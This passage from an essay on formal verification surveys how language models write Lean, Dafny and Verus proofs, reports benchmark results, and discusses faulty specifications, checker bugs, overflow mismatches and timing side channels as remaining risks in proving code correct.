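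Also in 2009, Xavier Leroy described CompCert, a compiler for most of the C language. He proved that the machine instructions it produces behave as the source program requires, so compiling a correct program doesn't introduce errors. The work took about three person-years.

At the rate of the seL4 proof, verifying a thousand lines of code would take more than two person-years. That may be acceptable for a small kernel that many other systems depend on, but not for code that changes every day.

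### Proofs written by language models

Language models have made some proofs much easier to produce. Researchers have mostly tested the models in Lean, the programming language Dafny, and Verus, a tool for Rust programs. In Dafny and Verus, the author adds hints such as invariants, and a solver tries to complete the proof. Lean requires a more explicit proof, and a small program called the kernel checks it.

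The vericoding benchmark was an early test of whether models could write programs and prove that they met given specifications. *Automating Formal Verification with Reinforcement Learning and Recursive Inference* (2026) reports that, in the initial results, at least one model succeeded on 82.2% of the Dafny tasks, 44.3% of the Verus tasks and 26.8% of the Lean tasks. These figures overstate what any one model could do. GPT-5, the best single model on Verus, succeeded on 30.9% of the Verus tasks.

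Not all specifications were carefully written. *Automating Formal Verification with Agent-Guided Tree Search* (2026) used only 423 of the Lean tasks, partly because many of the others had specifications that had been automatically translated from documentation or informal Python code. Even in two of the three groups it kept, a language model had translated the specifications into Lean from another language. A high success rate on such tasks shows that models can prove theorems, but not that the theorems describe what the programs were meant to do.

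*VeriContest* (2026) introduced a benchmark with specifications that experts had checked. It contains about a thousand problems from programming competitions. Each comes with a description in English, a specification, a Rust program that the competition's website had accepted, and a Verus proof that the program meets the specification. GPT-5.5 had the best results of the ten models tested:

| Task | Solved at the first attempt |
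|---|---|
| Write the program | 92.18% |
| Write the specification from the description | 48.31% |
| Prove that a given program meets a given specification | 13.95% |
| Do all three from the description | 5.29% |

By October 2026, five months after the benchmark appeared, writing proofs was no longer the main obstacle on these problems. Serbanuta, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *Solving VeriContest with a Lean-Backed Rust Verifier*, report that Claude Opus 5.5 proved that all 1,007 programs met their specifications. The researchers work for Asymptotic, the company that makes the verifier. They restated the problems as 1,325 theorems in Lean. The model could submit each proof up to 40 times and read the error messages after each attempt, but it couldn't change the program or the theorem, or add assumptions. The median proof took 3.4 minutes and cost $1.20, and the whole run cost $1,792.

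One of the programs reverses the digits of a number, or returns 0 if the result doesn't fit in 32 bits. It builds the answer one digit at a time in a loop. The model's invariant was that continuing from the current digits would always lead to the correct final answer. The model completed the proof, about 150 lines of Lean, in about two minutes.

This is a large improvement, but these programs are easier to verify than much of the code a reviewer receives. Each already had a Verus proof, so there was good reason to expect that a Lean proof existed. Code submitted for review might be wrong, and then no proof of its correctness is possible. Competition programs are also short and self-contained, whereas a proof about part of a large system must account for the other parts.

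The switch from Verus to Lean probably explains little of the improvement. Serbanuta and colleagues also gave Opus 5.5 the original Verus task for the 50 problems with the longest known proofs, allowing up to ten attempts at each. It solved 49, including 18 at the first attempt. A newer model and repeated feedback were enough for nearly all of these problems, although the model may have seen the Verus proofs, which had been public since May.

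### Proving the wrong thing

A proof shows only that a program meets its specification. If the specification for the clean-up script is that the cache folder is empty when the script finishes, a script that deletes every file on the machine would meet it.

*claimcheck* (Amster, Baker and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a specification for sorting a list that requires only that the output be in order. A program that always returns an empty list meets it, because nothing in an empty list is out of order. The paper's test set includes 182 textbook examples in Dafny that pass Dafny's verifier even though their specifications don't match their English descriptions. In one, the description is of a program that removes the first element of a list, but the specification requires it to remove the last.

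*Verus-SpecGym* (2026) explains that a verifier may certify a wrong program if the specification is too weak, and reject a correct one if it is too strong. Somebody may investigate a rejection, but a wrong program that meets a weak specification gets a valid proof, so there is no failure to prompt an investigation.

Wang, Yuan and colleagues (2026) provide evidence in *AuXSpec* on how often models make such mistakes. They used language models to write Lean specifications for 3,037 programming problems. For each problem, the models wrote one version convenient for proofs and, where necessary, another that a computer can run on test cases. The researchers kept a specification only if it passed the tests and other models judged that it matched the problem.

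Experts then reviewed 300 of the problems and found errors in 21, or 7%. In nine of those, the researchers could prove that the two versions of the specification agreed, but both contained the same misunderstanding of the problem. The experts also missed at least one error, which the researchers found when they tried to prove that the programs were correct.

Wang and colleagues also trained a model that produced an acceptable specification within four attempts for 84.3% of these problems, up from 14.3% before training. But they used tests and model judges to decide what was acceptable, and experts had found in the earlier review that specifications can pass both and still be wrong.

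Amster and colleagues tested whether a model can spot a faulty specification. When they showed a single model the English description and the specification together, it accepted some faulty specifications and rejected some correct ones, including 20% of the correct ones in the Dafny examples. They also argue that a model that has just read the description tends to judge that the specification matches it. Their tool therefore has one model explain the specification in English without seeing the original description, and another model compare the two English texts. On the Dafny examples, this method caught 94.5% of the faulty specifications and accepted 91.7% of the correct ones. In a related version of the tool, the advantage over using a single model almost disappeared when the judge was a stronger model.

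Running a specification on examples is another useful check. According to *AfterVibe* (2026), the *Verus-SpecGym* researchers found that this catches errors that model judges miss. In a similar check described in *AxDafny* (2026), researchers verified a program in Dafny, then translated it into Python and ran it on the original tests. A verified program that fails those tests may have a faulty specification, though the tests or the translation could also be wrong.

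### What else can go wrong

Kang and Kim argue that proving a program safe moves the remaining risk to the checker, the axioms behind the proof, the specification, and the match between the mathematical model and the real system.

Even widely used checkers have had bugs. Kang and Kim report that a 2026 release of Lean fixed a kernel bug found with the help of an OpenAI model. A later release fixed three more problems, one of which an OpenAI agent had used to construct two different "proofs" of a false statement. Anyone who can prove a false statement in Lean can use it to prove anything, including that a dangerous program is safe. Checking proofs with a second, independent checker reduces this risk, as does keeping the checker small enough for people to examine.

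The axioms behind a safety proof are probably what a company has least reason to worry about. A proof from contradictory axioms would be worthless, and by Gödel's second incompleteness theorem, a consistent system of this kind can't prove its own consistency. But if the axioms are consistent, any proof from them that a program never does something is enough to show that it never does. Suppose someone had proved that a script never deletes a file outside its folder, but it did so on some input. A record of that run would let us prove from the same axioms that the script can delete such a file, so the axioms would contradict each other. Mathematicians have studied and relied on the usual axioms for decades, while each new program needs a new safety claim.

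Guaranteeing that a proof's assumptions match the real system is harder. The proof for the clean-up script assumes that `/srv/app/cache` is an ordinary folder. If another program replaces it with a link to somebody's home folder, the script will delete the files there. The proof would still be valid, but it wouldn't apply because the folder is no longer an ordinary one.

Integer arithmetic can cause a similar mismatch. Trail of Bits asked three leading models to translate a C function that returns `n + 1` into Python, and all three wrote `n + 1`. Python's integers can grow without limit, but C's can't, and the C language doesn't define what happens when this addition overflows. A proof about the Python version would not cover the C version for the largest value of `n`. Serbanuta and colleagues compared their Lean translations with the original Rust programs on 19,555 test cases and found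 no differences, but those cases came from only 105 of the 1,007 programs.

Some properties are also missing from the usual models of a program. Suppose a program compares a password with the correct one letter by letter and stops at the first difference. An attacker who measures how long this takes can work out how many letters are right. A proof that the program always returns the right answer wouldn't reveal the problem, because a comparison that stops early returns the same answers as one that doesn't. To prevent the attack, the comparison must take the same time for every input, but Trail of Bits notes that most programming languages give programmers no way to state this requirement. Until recently, there was also no good way to make a compiler respect it, but Trail of Bits has written extensions to LLVM that do this.

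### Whether specifications are easier to review than code

A person may be able to review a short specification more reliably than a long program, at least when the specification is a prohibition. The rule "Never delete a file outside the cache folder" needs a careful definition of "outside", but the same definition works for every clean-up script, so a company can spend a week getting it right and then use it for years.

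Each program needs its own specification of everything it should do, and that specification may not be short. For the program that reverses digits, Serbanuta and colleagues print abridged versions of the code and the restated specification, and the specification is longer. The specification also reverses the digits step by step, much as the program does, so a reviewer who finds the program hard to follow won't find the specification much easier.

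Wang and colleagues' experts found 21 faulty problems that tests and models had missed, so careful review of specifications is worthwhile. But no one in the study reviewed ordinary code for the same problems, so the results don't show which kind of review is easier. A company's developers may also be less careful than experts who are preparing a benchmark.

Livshits thinks people will be the weak point in this kind of checking. One system he discusses, Astrogator, checks AI-written programs against a short formal request, which the user reads and confirms. In a test on 1,260 programs, it verified 83% of the correct ones and identified 92% of the incorrect ones. Developers still have to deal with the cases it can't settle, and Livshits argues that people who let AI write their code tend to accept whatever it proposes. If they approve a request without reading it properly, the system may verify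 a program that doesn't do what they wanted.

Who supplies the specification also matters. *The Specification as Quality Gate* (2026) reports small experiments with planted bugs. Every model tested missed a violation of a rule for medical codes, but an executable specification caught it. In another case, models confidently gave the wrong rule for aircraft fuel reserves. A model with the wrong rule could write it into both the program and the specification, and the proof would still succeed. Somebody who knows the right rule therefore has to check the specification, even if a machine can check everything else.
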